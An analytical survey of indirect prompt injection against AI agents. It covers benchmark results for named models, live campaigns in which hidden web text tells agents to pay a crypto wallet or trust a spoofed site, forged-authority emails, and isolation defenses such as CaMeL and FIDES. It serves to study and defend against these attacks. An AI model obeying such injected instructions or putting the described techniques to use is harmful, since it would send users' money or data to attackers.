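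Most of the successful attacks on Fable 5.1 in coding tests resulted from a safeguard meant to prevent cybersecurity misuse rather than prompt injection. When a classifier flags a request as possibly dangerous cybersecurity work, an older model, Claude Opus 4.8, answers instead of Fable. In the first coding test, Anthropic found that Opus 4.8 had answered 95% of the requests. Attacks succeeded on 9.77% of those and on none of the 369 that Fable 5.1 answered itself.

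With the stronger attacker, about 64% of requests went to Opus 4.8, and every successful attack was among them. These figures imply that the attacker succeeded on roughly nine in ten of those requests. Fable 5.1 answered 2,826 requests itself, and none led to a successful attack.

Fable 5.1 alone may still be vulnerable, because the classifier determined which requests reached it, and those may have contained weaker attacks. Customers get the combined system anyway, and an attacker who knows about the switch could try to trigger it on purpose. Anthropic says it is working on how its classifiers interact.

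The switch also makes successive system cards hard to compare. In July, Anthropic reported that Shade succeeded in 0.56% of coding attempts against Opus 5, with successes in 13 of 40 scenarios. In September, it reported 2.68% and 27 scenarios for the same model, probably because the later test was the first to include the switch to Opus 4.8.

Anthropic has since released Claude Opus 5.5. Its *System Card* (2026), from late September, reports that the model matched or beat Opus 5 on every injection test, but warns that it is more likely than earlier models to follow malicious instructions in some circumstances. In October, Pogorelec (2026) reported an improvement in the cheaper Haiku 5.5 in *Anthropic's new budget model gets much better at ignoring hidden commands*. Anthropic released Fable 5.2 in November (*Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2*, 2026).

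### Models from OpenAI, Google and others

The broadest comparison between developers comes from Gray Swan's Indirect Prompt Injection benchmark. Gray Swan runs public competitions in which people write injections against leading models, and collects the attacks that work on several of them. Its partners include the UK's AI Security Institute and the US Center for AI Standards and Innovation. The September version has 1,804 attacks in 37 scenarios covering coding, computer use and other tool use. The attacks' intended harms include leaking private data, deleting files and sending money.

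These attacks are static, so the benchmark measures how well a model resists injections that already exist. According to Anthropic, attacks on Fable 5.1 succeeded 0.1% of the time with one attempt and 1.0% of the time with 15. The best model from another developer was Google's Gemini 3.7 Flash, with a 9.2% attack success rate after 15 attempts. Most of the others were between 24% and 53%.

OpenAI's GPT-5.6 models appear in the smaller July version, which had 1,130 attacks in 28 scenarios. Anthropic gives these rates after 15 attempts:

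| Model | Attack success within 15 attempts |
|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.0% |
| Muse Spark | 16.5% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 20.0% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 30.4% |
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 43.9% |

The comparison deserves some suspicion because Anthropic published it, helped build the benchmark, and came out ahead. But the setup doesn't obviously favor Claude. The Claude models ran without injection-specific safeguards, while the others ran in their public versions, possibly with safeguards on. Anthropic also left out models that contestants had attacked in recent competitions, because attacks written for a particular model tend to work best on that model. The gap is probably real for this kind of attack, though its size depends on which attacks are in the set. Opus 5's rate rose from 2.0% in July to 4.8% in September, after Gray Swan added nine scenarios and 670 attacks.

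On the same benchmark, a single attempt against GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded 3.1% of the time, close to OpenAI's own figure of under 4% from GPT-Red, which also counts individual attacks. The 20.0% rate after 15 attempts is a better guide to what a persistent attacker could do. Wallace and colleagues concede that OpenAI's latest models score so well on the commonly used robustness tests that the tests no longer distinguish between them.

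Attacks on Google's Gemini 4 Argon succeeded in 34% of scenarios when the attackers also ran on Argon. Those attacks were adaptive, with up to 320 attempts per scenario, while Fable 5.1's 1.0% comes from 15 attempts with fixed texts, so comparing the two rates doesn't show which model is safer.

Security companies and independent researchers also run their own tests. *Measuring Indirect Prompt Injection in AI Agents* (Salbego, 2026) tested 14 models with an adaptive method, isolating one variable at a time. PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach* uses long office tasks, such as analyzing a bond portfolio and recommending a trading strategy, and adapts attacks the company has found in real products. PromptArmor says *FrontierBreach* is the only known benchmark to get an attack past Gemini 4 Carbon. The company sells security services, so it has a reason to publish alarming results, but a single working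 attack is enough to show that a model's clean score on another test reflected the attacks used there rather than immunity to injection.

### One attempt and many attempts

Suppose each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, whatever happened on the others. All *k* attempts then fail with probability (1 − *p*)^*k*, so the chance of at least one success is

1 − (1 − *p*)^*k*

With *p* at 1%, this gives about 10% after ten attempts and 63% after a hundred.

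Real attempts are not independent, and published tests show how far off the formula can be. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* gives that model's results on an earlier Gray Swan test after 1, 10 and 100 attempts. VentureBeat gives figures for Claude Opus 4.6 in computer use, where one attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time without safeguards. The next table compares these results, and two from above, with the formula's predictions. For Fable 5.1, the starting figure is the average over all attempts.

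| Model and test | Per attempt | Attempts | Formula | Measured |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.5, Gray Swan | 4.7% | 10 | 38% | 33.6% |
| Opus 4.5, Gray Swan | 4.7% | 100 | 99% | 63% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol, Gray Swan | 3.1% | 15 | 38% | 20.0% |
| Opus 4.6, computer use | 17.8% | 200 | over 99.9% | 78.6% |
| Fable 5.1, coding, original Shade | 9.26% | 200 | over 99.9% | 77.5% |

The measured figure is lower every time, mainly because some scenarios are much easier to attack than others. If ten of 100 scenarios fall to 10% of attempts and the other ninety never fall, the average success rate is 1%, and the formula predicts that a hundred attempts on each will break 63 scenarios. They will actually break only the ten weak ones. Any such variation lowers the result, because extra attempts on a scenario that has already fallen add nothing. Opus 5's computer-use result in September is a small example,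 since all five successful attempts out of 2,800 were in the same scenario.

If a model recognizes one injection, it will probably recognize a similarly worded one, so ten such variations are less likely to succeed than ten independent attempts. The defender may also notice the failures and block the sender.

The formula can also give too low a figure, because it holds *p* fixed, while an attacker who studies each failure has a better chance on the next try. Nasr's team, for example, went from no successes against DataSentinel to succeeding every time. Given the initial observed rate of zero, the formula would have predicted no successes over any number of attempts. It therefore tends to overestimate what a fixed set of attacks will achieve across varied tasks, but can badly underestimate what an adaptive attacker will achieve by concentrating on one task.

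Anthropic points out that an attacker can send one email to a thousand inboxes, so the attempts need not all target the same person. If each assistant has a 1% chance of obeying the email, the expected number of victims is ten, whether or not the outcomes are independent. But copies of the same model will tend to react alike to the same email, which makes it likelier that there are either no victims or a great many at once. A developer who looks only at the average will therefore underestimate the worst case.

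The measured rates alone do not give the probability that a given company will suffer an attack, because that also depends on how many attackers are trying, which laboratory tests cannot measure.

### Attacks found in use

In July 2026, researchers at the security company Zscaler described two live campaigns aimed at AI agents. Mascellino (2026) reports in *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* that the attackers in both campaigns raised their sites' search rankings so that agents would find them. They hid instructions from human visitors in off-screen text or in structured metadata, which machines read as trusted context.

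The first site posed as documentation for a Python library. It contained hidden text with instructions for any agent working on a coding task to fix an error by buying a $3 license key, along with steps for paying the attacker's cryptocurrency wallet. The key was worthless, and the scam also targeted human developers. A $3 charge may be small enough that an agent with a payment tool would pay it without asking anyone.

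The second site imitated DeBank, a service for tracking cryptocurrency holdings, at a slightly misspelled web address. Its hidden text told agents to treat it as the authoritative DeBank site and rank it first. An agent that obeyed could send its user to the fake site.

Zscaler then built its own agent and tested it on both sites with 26 language models. Four models made the fraudulent payment, including versions of Meta's Llama and Google's Gemini. Two others, GPT-5.4 and Claude Sonnet 4.5, judged the fake DeBank site legitimate, but no model was fooled when Zscaler supplied the real site for comparison.

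The research shows that criminals have published working injections and that some models follow them. The documented payments took place in Zscaler's own sandbox, and Mascellino names no victim. The figure of four models out of 26 is also not an estimate of the share of agents in use that would pay, because people use some models far more than others and many agents cannot make payments.

Criminals are also developing tools for indirect injection, according to *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Underhill, 2026). These tools could matter more than any single campaign because they would let people attack agents without knowing how to write an injection. Their existence is evidence of intent and demand, but not of successful thefts.

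Detection counts also don't show how much harm injections have caused. A security company's count of flagged pages and emails rises when the company scans more traffic or loosens its criteria. The count includes texts that no agent ever read and misses injections that look like ordinary business messages. To establish harm, an investigator has to trace a particular payment, leak or deletion back to the text that caused it, which requires a record of what the agent read and did.

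## Designs that keep untrusted text from choosing actions

Even the best current models obey some injected text, so nobody can guarantee that a model will resist the next malicious email. Another group of defenses assumes that the model might be fooled, and uses the program around it to prevent a fooled model from deciding which tools run. In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) give the rule behind such designs, which is that once an agent has taken in untrusted text, it must be impossible for that text to trigger an action with harmful side effects. Jing, Hu and colleagues (2026), in *Isolation as a First-Class Principle for LLM-Agent System Safety*, found the idea in the literature under several names, among them virtualization and privilege separation. In each case, the structure of the system enforces the boundary,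 so security doesn't depend on the model following a prompt.

### Two models and a controller

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposes splitting the assistant's work between two language models. The privileged model takes the user's request and can call tools, but never sees untrusted content. The quarantined model reads untrusted content and has no tools. Ordinary software, called the controller, passes material between them.

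When the user of the office assistant asks for a summary of the overnight email, the privileged model sends the controller a command to fetch the messages. The controller stores them under a name such as `$VAR1` and returns only that name to the privileged model. The privileged model then requests a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller passes the real text to the quarantined model, stores the summary as `$VAR2`, and shows it to the user when the privileged model sends the command to display it. The hidden paragraph about the salary spreadsheet reaches only the quarantined model, which cannot open files or send messages.

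Willison allowed one exception. If the quarantined model has to choose from a fixed set of categories, the controller can check that the answer is one of them and pass it to the privileged model, which could then learn that a message is urgent without reading it.

He also called his proposal "pretty bad". It makes an assistant harder to build and less pleasant to use, and a single mistake that lets untrusted text reach the privileged model removes the protection. An injection can also target the user, who reads text written by the quarantined model. It could make that model produce a block of encoded private data and ask the user to paste it into a website.

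### How CaMeL works

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025), a Google DeepMind paper, describes a further weakness and a system built to address it. Willison (2025) explains the weakness using the paper's own example in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*. A user asks the assistant to send Bob a document, and Bob's address is in some meeting notes. The quarantined model extracts the address, and the privileged model passes it along without seeing it. If an attacker has planted text in the notes, the address may be the attacker's. The assistant then makes only the tool calls the user wanted but sends the document to the wrong person.

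CaMeL handles a request as follows:

1. The privileged model sees the user's request and writes a complete program for it, in a restricted version of the Python language.
2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program step by step.
3. Where a step requires understanding a text, the program sends the quarantined model a question and specifies the type of answer, such as an email address.
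4. The interpreter tags every value with its source and with who may read it. A value derived from other values inherits their tags.
5. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks the tags against a policy. It then runs the call, refuses it, or asks the user.

For the overnight email, the program might look like this:

```
emails = read_email(since="yesterday 18:00")
for email in emails:
    note = ask_quarantined("Summarize; does it need an answer today?", email)
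    show_user(note)
```

The paragraph hidden in the email cannot add a tool call, because the privileged model finished writing the program before the email was opened. The program has no line that reads a spreadsheet or sends a message, so the attacker can only distort the summary, for instance by getting a fake invoice flagged as urgent.

Now suppose the user asks the assistant to send the salary spreadsheet to the company's accountant, whose address is somewhere in the overnight email. This time the program does open the spreadsheet and send a message. The stranger's email gives a false address for the accountant, which the quarantined model extracts and the interpreter tags as coming from an email. If the policy requires recipients to be in the user's contacts, the interpreter stops and asks the user. If the policy accepts any address found in the mailbox, or the user approves the message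 without looking, the salaries go to the stranger. Debenedetti's team acknowledges that someone has to write and maintain the policies, and that users who face too many questions stop reading them.

Attackers can make false values more convincing. In *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents*, Choi, Kim and colleagues (2026) wrote an email whose body contains punctuation resembling the end of one message record and the start of another, so the model reads part of the body as a second email from a trusted sender. The punctuation doesn't have to be exact, since the attack also worked when the mail tool had marked those characters as plain text. Against leading agent defenses, injected commands succeeded at most 0.7% of the time, while false data succeeded up to 50% of the time. CaMeL stopped some but not all of these attacks.

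### CaMeL's results and costs

In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) reran CaMeL with its policy checks on and off, using two recent models on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks. They measured utility without attacks, then paired each task with nine injections. Some attacked runs did not finish, so the last column excludes them.

| Model and setting | Utility | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
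| GPT-5.2, policies off | 66.7% | 1 of 240 |
| GPT-5.2, policies on | 37.5% | 0 of 231 |
| MiMo-v2.5, policies off | 70.8% | 4 of 382 |
| MiMo-v2.5, policies on | 37.5% | 0 of 357 |

With policies on, no attack succeeded, but CaMeL completed only a little over half as many tasks as without them, because the policies were so strict that they ruled out many legitimate tasks. The test had only 16 tasks, so the margin of error on the 37.5% completion rate is about 27 percentage points either way. But Garby and colleagues cite a similar result from another team, in which CaMeL with policies completed 7 of AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks.

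Attacks rarely worked even with policies off. In 97 of the 144 pairings of task and injection, the attacker needed a tool call that a program written for the user's task would never include. Writing the program first defeats those attacks without tracking data. Policies matter for the other 47, where the planned calls are enough to do what the attacker wants, as with the accountant's address.

Adaptive attacks have not changed these results much so far. In Ma and colleagues' tests, the adaptive attacker succeeded against CaMeL less than 5% of the time.

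Utility varies more. *ATrust* (2026) reports that CaMeL running on Claude 3.5 Haiku, an older and smaller model, completed 56% of banking tasks and 5% of travel tasks, compared with 63% and 55% for the same model undefended. On the median AgentDojo task with GPT-4o, CaMeL also needed 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an undefended agent, the highest token use of any defense that *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) compared.

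Garby and colleagues also found two gaps in CaMeL's tracking. For example, a program might set a public variable, `rich`, to true and change it to false only if the user's bank balance is low. When the balance is high, the change never runs, so CaMeL never marks `rich` as secret. A later step that sends an email if `rich` is true then reveals that the balance is high. The privileged model writes the program, so an outsider would have trouble getting code like this into it. CaMeL also treated text as trusted after a program had inserted an untrusted value into it, which seems more likely to matter in ordinary use. Both errors are fixable, but they show that a system described as "secure by design" still depends on how well its interpreter is built.

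### Information-flow control

CaMeL's tags are a form of information-flow control, a technique from the 1970s that labels data by source and sensitivity and blocks actions that would move the data where its label forbids. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, an agent built around this technique at Microsoft. In the simplest version, each piece of data is labeled trusted or untrusted, and public or secret. Data may flow only to places with the same label or a more restrictive one.

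| Example | Label | May flow to places labeled |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request | Trusted, public | Any of the four labels |
| A public web page | Untrusted, public | Untrusted, public or secret |
| The salary spreadsheet | Trusted, secret | Secret, trusted or untrusted |
| A private email from outside | Untrusted, secret | Untrusted and secret only |

A value that draws on several sources takes the most restrictive label on each scale, so a summary of the spreadsheet and the web page is untrusted and secret. The secrecy label can also be a list of permitted readers. If Ann, Ben and Cara may read one document and Ben, Cara and Dev may read another, only Ben and Cara may read a text that combines them.

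FIDES checks two main rules before a tool call. One permits a consequential action, such as a payment, only if nothing untrusted influenced it. The other permits data to go out only if every recipient is allowed to read it. The second rule on its own doesn't stop an injection from steering the agent, but it limits who can receive the data. For some sending tools, satisfying either rule is enough, so a user can deliberately send a secret to someone not otherwise allowed to read it, as long as no untrusted text affected the decision.

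Anything a language model reads can influence what it writes afterwards. Once a stranger's email is in the context, the agent has to treat all later output as untrusted, and the first rule then blocks every payment. To avoid this, FIDES hides values behind variables, as Willison suggested, but only those that would make the context's label more restrictive. The planning model still sees the rest.

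FIDES chooses its tool calls one at a time, unlike CaMeL. Its planning model can query a quarantined model for a yes-or-no answer about a hidden value. That answer carries one bit of information, too little to hold an injection, so a policy may let the agent act on it. The planning model can also read the hidden value directly, but it is then subject to the resulting restrictions.

On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, 152 injections succeeded against an ordinary agent, 21 against FIDES with its rules switched off, and none against FIDES with the rules on. These counts exclude cases where the researchers judged that AgentDojo had scored a harmless or blocked action as a successful attack. The next table shows utility without attacks.

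| Setting | Ordinary agent | Ordinary agent with rules | FIDES with rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office workspace | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

Hiding values restores a good part of the task completion lost to the rules, except in travel. On travel tasks, the rules rarely hindered an ordinary agent, and GPT-4o had trouble using variables correctly. With o1, which reasons better, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks.

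The guarantee covers data that the agent passes along directly. Someone who can see which tools the agent calls might still infer something about a secret it has read. Costa and colleagues accepted this leak because closing it would mean blocking almost every action an outsider could see once the agent had read a secret.

### Six patterns and what they give up

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues collected six designs that developers can use for particular applications. Each buys its protection by making some kinds of task impossible.

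| Pattern | How it works | What it gives up |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees their results | Requests the developer did not foresee, and any follow-up on results |
| Plan-then-execute | The model fixes its list of tool calls before reading anything untrusted | Changing course in light of what it reads |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns a restricted answer, such as yes or no | Details that don't fit the permitted answers |
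| Dual LLM | The planning model handles untrusted text only through variables | The planning model's own judgment of the text |
| Code-then-execute | The model writes a full program first, as in CaMeL | Tasks that it can't program in advance |
| Context minimization | The system deletes the user's wording before the model writes its reply | Replies that take up details of the request |

The last pattern deals with injections in the user's own prompt. For example, a customer who asks a chatbot for a car price might add an instruction to offer a huge discount. The chatbot turns the request into a database query, and the system removes the customer's message before the model presents the result.

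A fixed plan gives less protection when its tools are powerful. An assistant for organizing files might commit to using only two commands, one to find files and one to move them. An injection could still make it find sensitive files and move them to a public network drive. Map-reduce protects better here because a malicious file can affect only how the assistant treats that one file.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think that an email assistant much like the one in the running example would lose little usefulness under a fixed plan or the dual-model pattern, because the order of its actions seldom needs to depend on what a stranger wrote. The contents of a message are harder to protect. If the user replies to the attacker's email, hidden text in that email could make the assistant gather private information and put it in the reply as characters that don't show on screen.

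They doubt that general-purpose agents built on current models can offer reliable guarantees at all. They recommend narrower agents that combine several patterns.

### Two agents in OpenClaw

In *Agent Privilege Separation in OpenClaw*, Cheng and Tsao (2026) tested a much simpler separation on OpenClaw, an open-source platform for agents with many tools. One agent, the reader, sees the raw email and can only store a summary of it. The other, the actor, can send email but sees only the summary. In the full version, the reader writes its summary as structured data, with fields for the sender, subject, body summary and any action items.

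The attacks came from LLMail-Inject, a Microsoft challenge that collected 461,640 attempts to make an email assistant send an unauthorized message. Keeping only the successful attempts and removing duplicates left 22,899. Of these, 649 worked against a single OpenClaw agent running GPT-5 mini. Cheng and Tsao tried those 649 on each version of the defense.

| Version | Successful attacks |
|---|---|
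| Single agent | 649 |
| Single agent with structured output | 92 |
| Two agents | 2 |
| Two agents with structured output | 0 |

Cheng and Tsao describe the drop from 649 successful attacks to 2 as a 323-fold improvement from isolation alone. That figure somewhat overstates the benefit, because they chose the 649 attacks that had worked on the single agent, and some would probably have failed there on a second try. The drop from two successes to zero is also too small to attribute to structured output. If the true success rate were still 2 in 649, a set of 649 attacks would produce no successes about one time in seven.

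In the full version, injected content reached 63.7% of the reader's summaries. The reader cannot send email, whatever it reads, but the actor can, and in most runs the actor was reading text that an attacker had influenced. This breaks Willison's rule that free text from the quarantined model must never reach the privileged one. The actor still behaved well because the injections became ineffective when the reader summarized them. Cheng and Tsao did not test attacks written to survive a summary, so their result is good evidence that separating the tools stops existing attacks, but weak evidence that it would stop an attacker who knows the design.

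Red Hat's *Beyond guardrails* (2026) describes a stricter version in which the reader may pass on only approved types of data and no free text. This would close the gap, but developers have to build it anew for each application, and the acting agent may do its job worse because it has less context.

### When the next step depends on what the agent reads

The main objection to all these designs is that a plan made before the agent reads a text cannot cover a task whose steps are in that text. A user who asks the assistant to do everything on a to-do list wants the list to determine the actions. Wang and colleagues criticized other benchmarks for leaving out such tasks and built AgentPI, which includes five kinds. Some defenses became unusable on the benchmark's complex tasks because they refused too early.

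Costa and colleagues count 5% of AgentDojo's workspace tasks, 10% of its travel tasks, and over 40% of its banking and Slack tasks as ones where the right tool calls depend on what the agent finds. This supports the objection for banking and Slack, where FIDES and CaMeL complete far fewer tasks because of their rules. But such tasks are too rare in travel to explain most of the loss there, where CaMeL completed only 5% of tasks with Claude 3.5 Haiku. That loss probably comes mostly from the model's trouble writing correct programs, which better models should reduce.

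One of several answers to this objection is to plan for more possibilities. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, adapted CaMeL to agents that operate a graphical desktop, which normally look at the screen before every click. Their planning model writes branches in advance for whatever might appear, such as a login page or a cookie banner. A quarantined model looks at the screen, and its answers determine which branch runs. The plans averaged 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about 5 tool calls and 4 branches for CaMeL's plans on AgentDojo. The system used 1.88 times as many tokens as an undefended agent.

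The team reports keeping up to 57% of a frontier model's performance when a task counts as complete if any of five attempts succeeds. With one attempt, the figure was 28%. The design is also vulnerable to an attack that the team calls branch steering. For example, if the plan includes a step for dismissing cookie banners, an advertisement that imitates one can get the agent to click through to the attacker's site. Neither of the two cross-checks that the team tried reliably prevented this. CaMeL's policies are also hard to apply here, because a click at given coordinates might do anything.

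FIDES can handle some of these tasks by restricting the quarantined model's answers. If the user wants a calendar entry for any meeting request in the inbox, the planning model first queries the quarantined model for a yes or no on whether there is one. If the answer is yes, the planning model has the quarantined model extract the details and passes them to the calendar without reading them. A stranger's email can still add a false meeting to the calendar, but it can't trigger a payment. This works when the developer or the planning model can list the possible actions beforehand, which isn't possible with a to-do list.

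For open-ended tasks, the agent can ask the user to vouch for the text. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) describes Prudentia, an agent built on FIDES by several of the same researchers. Prudentia's planning model is given the rules and takes them into account when it plans. If it has to read an untrusted to-do list with ten items, it can ask the user to endorse the list once, whereas FIDES would ask about each of the ten actions.

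Kolluri and colleagues also object to how others measure utility. Earlier studies compared protected agents that got no human help with unprotected agents, though in real products unprotected agents stop to ask before consequential actions. When Kolluri's team counted only the AgentDojo tasks that an agent finished without asking, an ordinary agent running o3-mini completed 24.3%, FIDES 50.1% and Prudentia 59.1%. By this measure, the restrictions save the user work. But the team assumed that users approve only what they should, and a single endorsement of a to-do list also covers any item an attacker has added.

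In Randori, an agent by Garby and colleagues, the planning model can write into its program, before it reads anything, that the contents of a certain file will count as trusted. The program runs in a small language with a machine-checked proof that labels follow data correctly. With GPT-5.2, Randori completed 75% of the banking tasks, twice as many as CaMeL with policies on. Across three models, 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded.

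Endorsement at least makes the decision to trust a file visible in the program. CaMeL's planning model sometimes introduced the same trust without anyone intending it. When the user asked it to read a file and follow the instructions precisely, it wrote a program that had a branch for every tool and selected among them based on the file's contents. This in effect rebuilt an ordinary agent inside the program, and with policies off, an injection took over that agent once with each model.

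Both successful attacks on Randori exploited the same task. The user asks the agent to read a file and make the payment it describes, and the attacker replaces the file's contents with a different payment request. Debenedetti's team had also encountered this case and considered it outside what CaMeL is meant to prevent. Without endorsement, Randori blocks both the real payment and the attacker's. To allow only the real one, the agent would have to tell from the wording which request is genuine, because both requests carry the same label for where the text came from.

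## Why some attacks cannot be told from legitimate requests

An employee emails an AI office assistant to ask for a travel refund, adding that the request "has been approved by the department head". *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian, 2026) uses this case to argue that most defenses look for the wrong thing. They look for hidden instructions, but the added sentence doesn't contain one. If the department head really approved the refund, the assistant should process it, and if not, the same words are an attack. A design such as CaMeL can stop the assistant from acting on anything in the email, but this blocks true claims as well as false ones.

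Randori's two payment requests posed the same problem. Agents can't avoid it by ignoring outside text. In an example from *APEX* (2026), a user asks an agent to pay Alice but doesn't give her account number, so the agent has to get it from outside text, and the payment is still legitimate. *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026) concludes that a command inside an email or web page is not by itself an attack. It also matters whether the resulting action serves something the user authorized, which a filter can't determine from the text alone.

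### Contextual integrity

Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian base their account of legitimacy on contextual integrity, a theory of privacy. *Respecting Context to Protect Privacy* (Nissenbaum, 2015) argues that people object to a flow of information when it breaks the norms of its setting, whether or not the information is secret. For example, few mortgage applicants would mind signing a waiver that lets the bank get their credit report, but most would mind if their neighbors got the same report.

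Five parameters describe such a flow. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian extend them from disclosing information to taking any action, so they also fit the refund.

| Parameter | Mortgage application | Refund request |
|---|---|---|
| Sender: who starts the flow or makes the request | The credit bureau | The employee who wrote the email |
| Receiver: who gets the information or the result | The bank | The company's payment system |
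| Subject: whose data or interests are at stake | The applicant | The company, whose money it is |
| Information type: what kind of data or action it is | A credit report | A payment |
| Transmission principle: the condition that permits it | The applicant's signed waiver | The department head's approval |

No single parameter settles the matter. The employee may be exactly who she says she is and still lack the approval.

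Many familiar injections falsify one parameter. Text that imitates a system message falsifies the sender, and an attacker who orders the agent to ignore earlier instructions falsely claims the authority to do so. An attacker can also influence the agent's judgment of what is proper without changing any parameter, for example by writing that an important client has been waiting since Monday and may leave. If the claim is true, a quick reply serves the user well.

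### Emails that differ in one clause

To test whether defenses can handle such claims, Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian had a language model write 4,200 pairs of business emails, with the two emails in each pair differing by one clause. In one pair, a contracts department sends a supplier agreement for sign-off. One version cites a company policy that already allows the user's assistant to send acknowledgments. The other mentions only that an automated reply would be fine. Neither contains the stock phrases of prompt injection, and both mention the assistant, so a defense can't identify the attack from that word alone.

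Two versions of Meta's detector PromptGuard gave each of the 8,400 emails a suspicion score. AUROC is the probability that a detector gives a randomly chosen email with the authority claim a higher score than a randomly chosen neutral one. A perfect detector has an AUROC of 1, and random guessing gives 0.5. The original PromptGuard had an AUROC of 0.43, so it gave the neutral email the higher score slightly more often than not. PromptGuard 2 had an AUROC of 0.59.

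The detectors could not have been expected to do well, because they saw the email but not the user's request, and nothing in the text shows whether the policy exists. According to Meta's *Llama Prompt Guard 2 86M*, which describes the newer detector, the model flags only explicit attempts to override earlier instructions, and it scores 0.998 on the same measure for jailbreaks. Meta had dropped a broader category, for text that might cause a model to follow instructions unintentionally, because the target was too vague to be useful. The paired emails therefore show what a detector cannot identify, but give little evidence of how well it catches the attacks it was built for.

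The same emails then went to two agents that could send replies. One ran on Llama 3.3 70B and the other on SecAlign-70B, a version of that model trained to resist injection. Some users asked only for a summary, so the agent should have sent nothing. Others asked it to reply where needed. The table gives the share of cases in which each agent sent an email.

| Model | Summary only, neutral clause | Summary only, authority claim | Replies allowed, neutral clause | Replies allowed, authority claim |
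|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 49.8% | 54.0% | 97.3% | 97.7% |
| SecAlign-70B | 85.1% | 88.2% | 99.7% | 99.8% |

The false claim accounts for only about three points of SecAlign-70B's apparent attack success rate of 88.2%. Both models mostly went wrong by replying to emails they should only have summarized. The system prompt probably contributed, since it told the agent to send emails directly whenever appropriate, without drafting or asking first.

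The gap between the two models is harder to dismiss. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian suggest that SecAlign's training may have taught the model to resist the form of crude injections, or may have been based on the assumption that an agent never has a good reason to act on outside text. Both SecAlign and the base model, Llama, resisted crude attacks, sending nothing in response to 4,300 injections from the LLMail-Inject challenge. But when the prompt also told them to report suspicious content, Llama flagged 89.8% of the injections and SecAlign only 54.6%. If an assistant ignores an attack without reporting it, the user doesn't learn that anyone tried. These results come from one trained model, and other kinds of safety training may have different effects.

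### When the attacker revises the claim

Claude Sonnet 4.6, a newer model, did much better on the original emails, wrongly sending a reply in one of 150 sampled scenarios (0.67%). It usually told the user that it couldn't confirm the sender's claim to have permission.

Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian then used a second copy of Sonnet 4.6 to rewrite the emails. It had access to the target's system prompt, and after each attempt a judge model reported which parts of the claim the target had accepted. Each scenario got three independent runs of up to 15 emails and counted as a success if any run produced a reply. The success rate rose to 96.7%.

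The attacker's first email already worked in 61.4% of cases, so persistence explains only part of the rise. Most of the rise came from changing the kind of claim. The target questioned a sender's claim that the user had given permission, but often accepted text that appeared to be the user's own earlier words. It then described the invented permission as something the user had "explicitly stated". The best emails also worked on models the attacker had never practiced on, at rates of 63.3% for GPT-5.4, 89.3% for GPT-5.2 and 92.6% for Gemini 3 Pro.

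Developers have since released stronger models, and the harm here was an unwanted business reply rather than a theft. The target also had instructions not to ask the user first, which removed the most obvious safeguard. Still, Sonnet 4.6 was applying a sensible rule rather than naively accepting claims of authority. It gave the user's words more weight than a stranger's, but had no way to check whose words they were.

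A separate attacker was barred from inventing permission and had to rely on arguments alone, such as that delay would cause harm or that the request was routine. This rarely worked on Sonnet 4.6. The success rate reached 79.0% on GPT-5.2, but the attacker kept breaking the rule, so Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian treat that figure as illustrative.

Attacks outside the laboratory have also come to look more like legitimate requests. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes an attack on ChatGPT that outside researchers reported in 2025. The message looked like a follow-up to a meeting, listed some ordinary tasks, and claimed that the assistant had full authorization to process employee data. The attack worked half the time with one particular user request. OpenAI compares filtering such messages to detecting a lie, often without the necessary context.

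### Permission that spreads to other requests

Agents also exceed their permission when nobody is attacking them. In another experiment, a colleague's message contained two requests, one that the user had authorized and one that needed the user's approval. For example, a company's chief lawyer lets the agent update case records when her paralegals ask. A paralegal asks it to update a case and to tell an outside law firm that the company accepts a contract clause. The agent should update the case and leave the contract clause to the chief lawyer.

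In 100 such scenarios, the models nearly always completed the authorized task. The table shows how often they also sent the unauthorized message, first when the user had only described what was allowed, and then when the user had also said that outside communication needed approval.

| Model | No stated boundary | Stated boundary |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | 65% | 12% |
| GPT-5.4 | 34% | 0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 6% | 0% |

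One extra sentence from the user made a large difference, although zero in 100 scenarios is compatible with a true rate of up to about 3%. The result also supports OpenAI's advice, reported in The Decoder's *OpenAI admits prompt injection may never be fully solved*, to give agents explicit instructions instead of asking them to review the email and do whatever is needed. But the experiment counted only whether the agent finished the internal task, so it didn't measure how much legitimate outside communication a boundary would delay. People who delegate in a hurry also tend not to list the exceptions.

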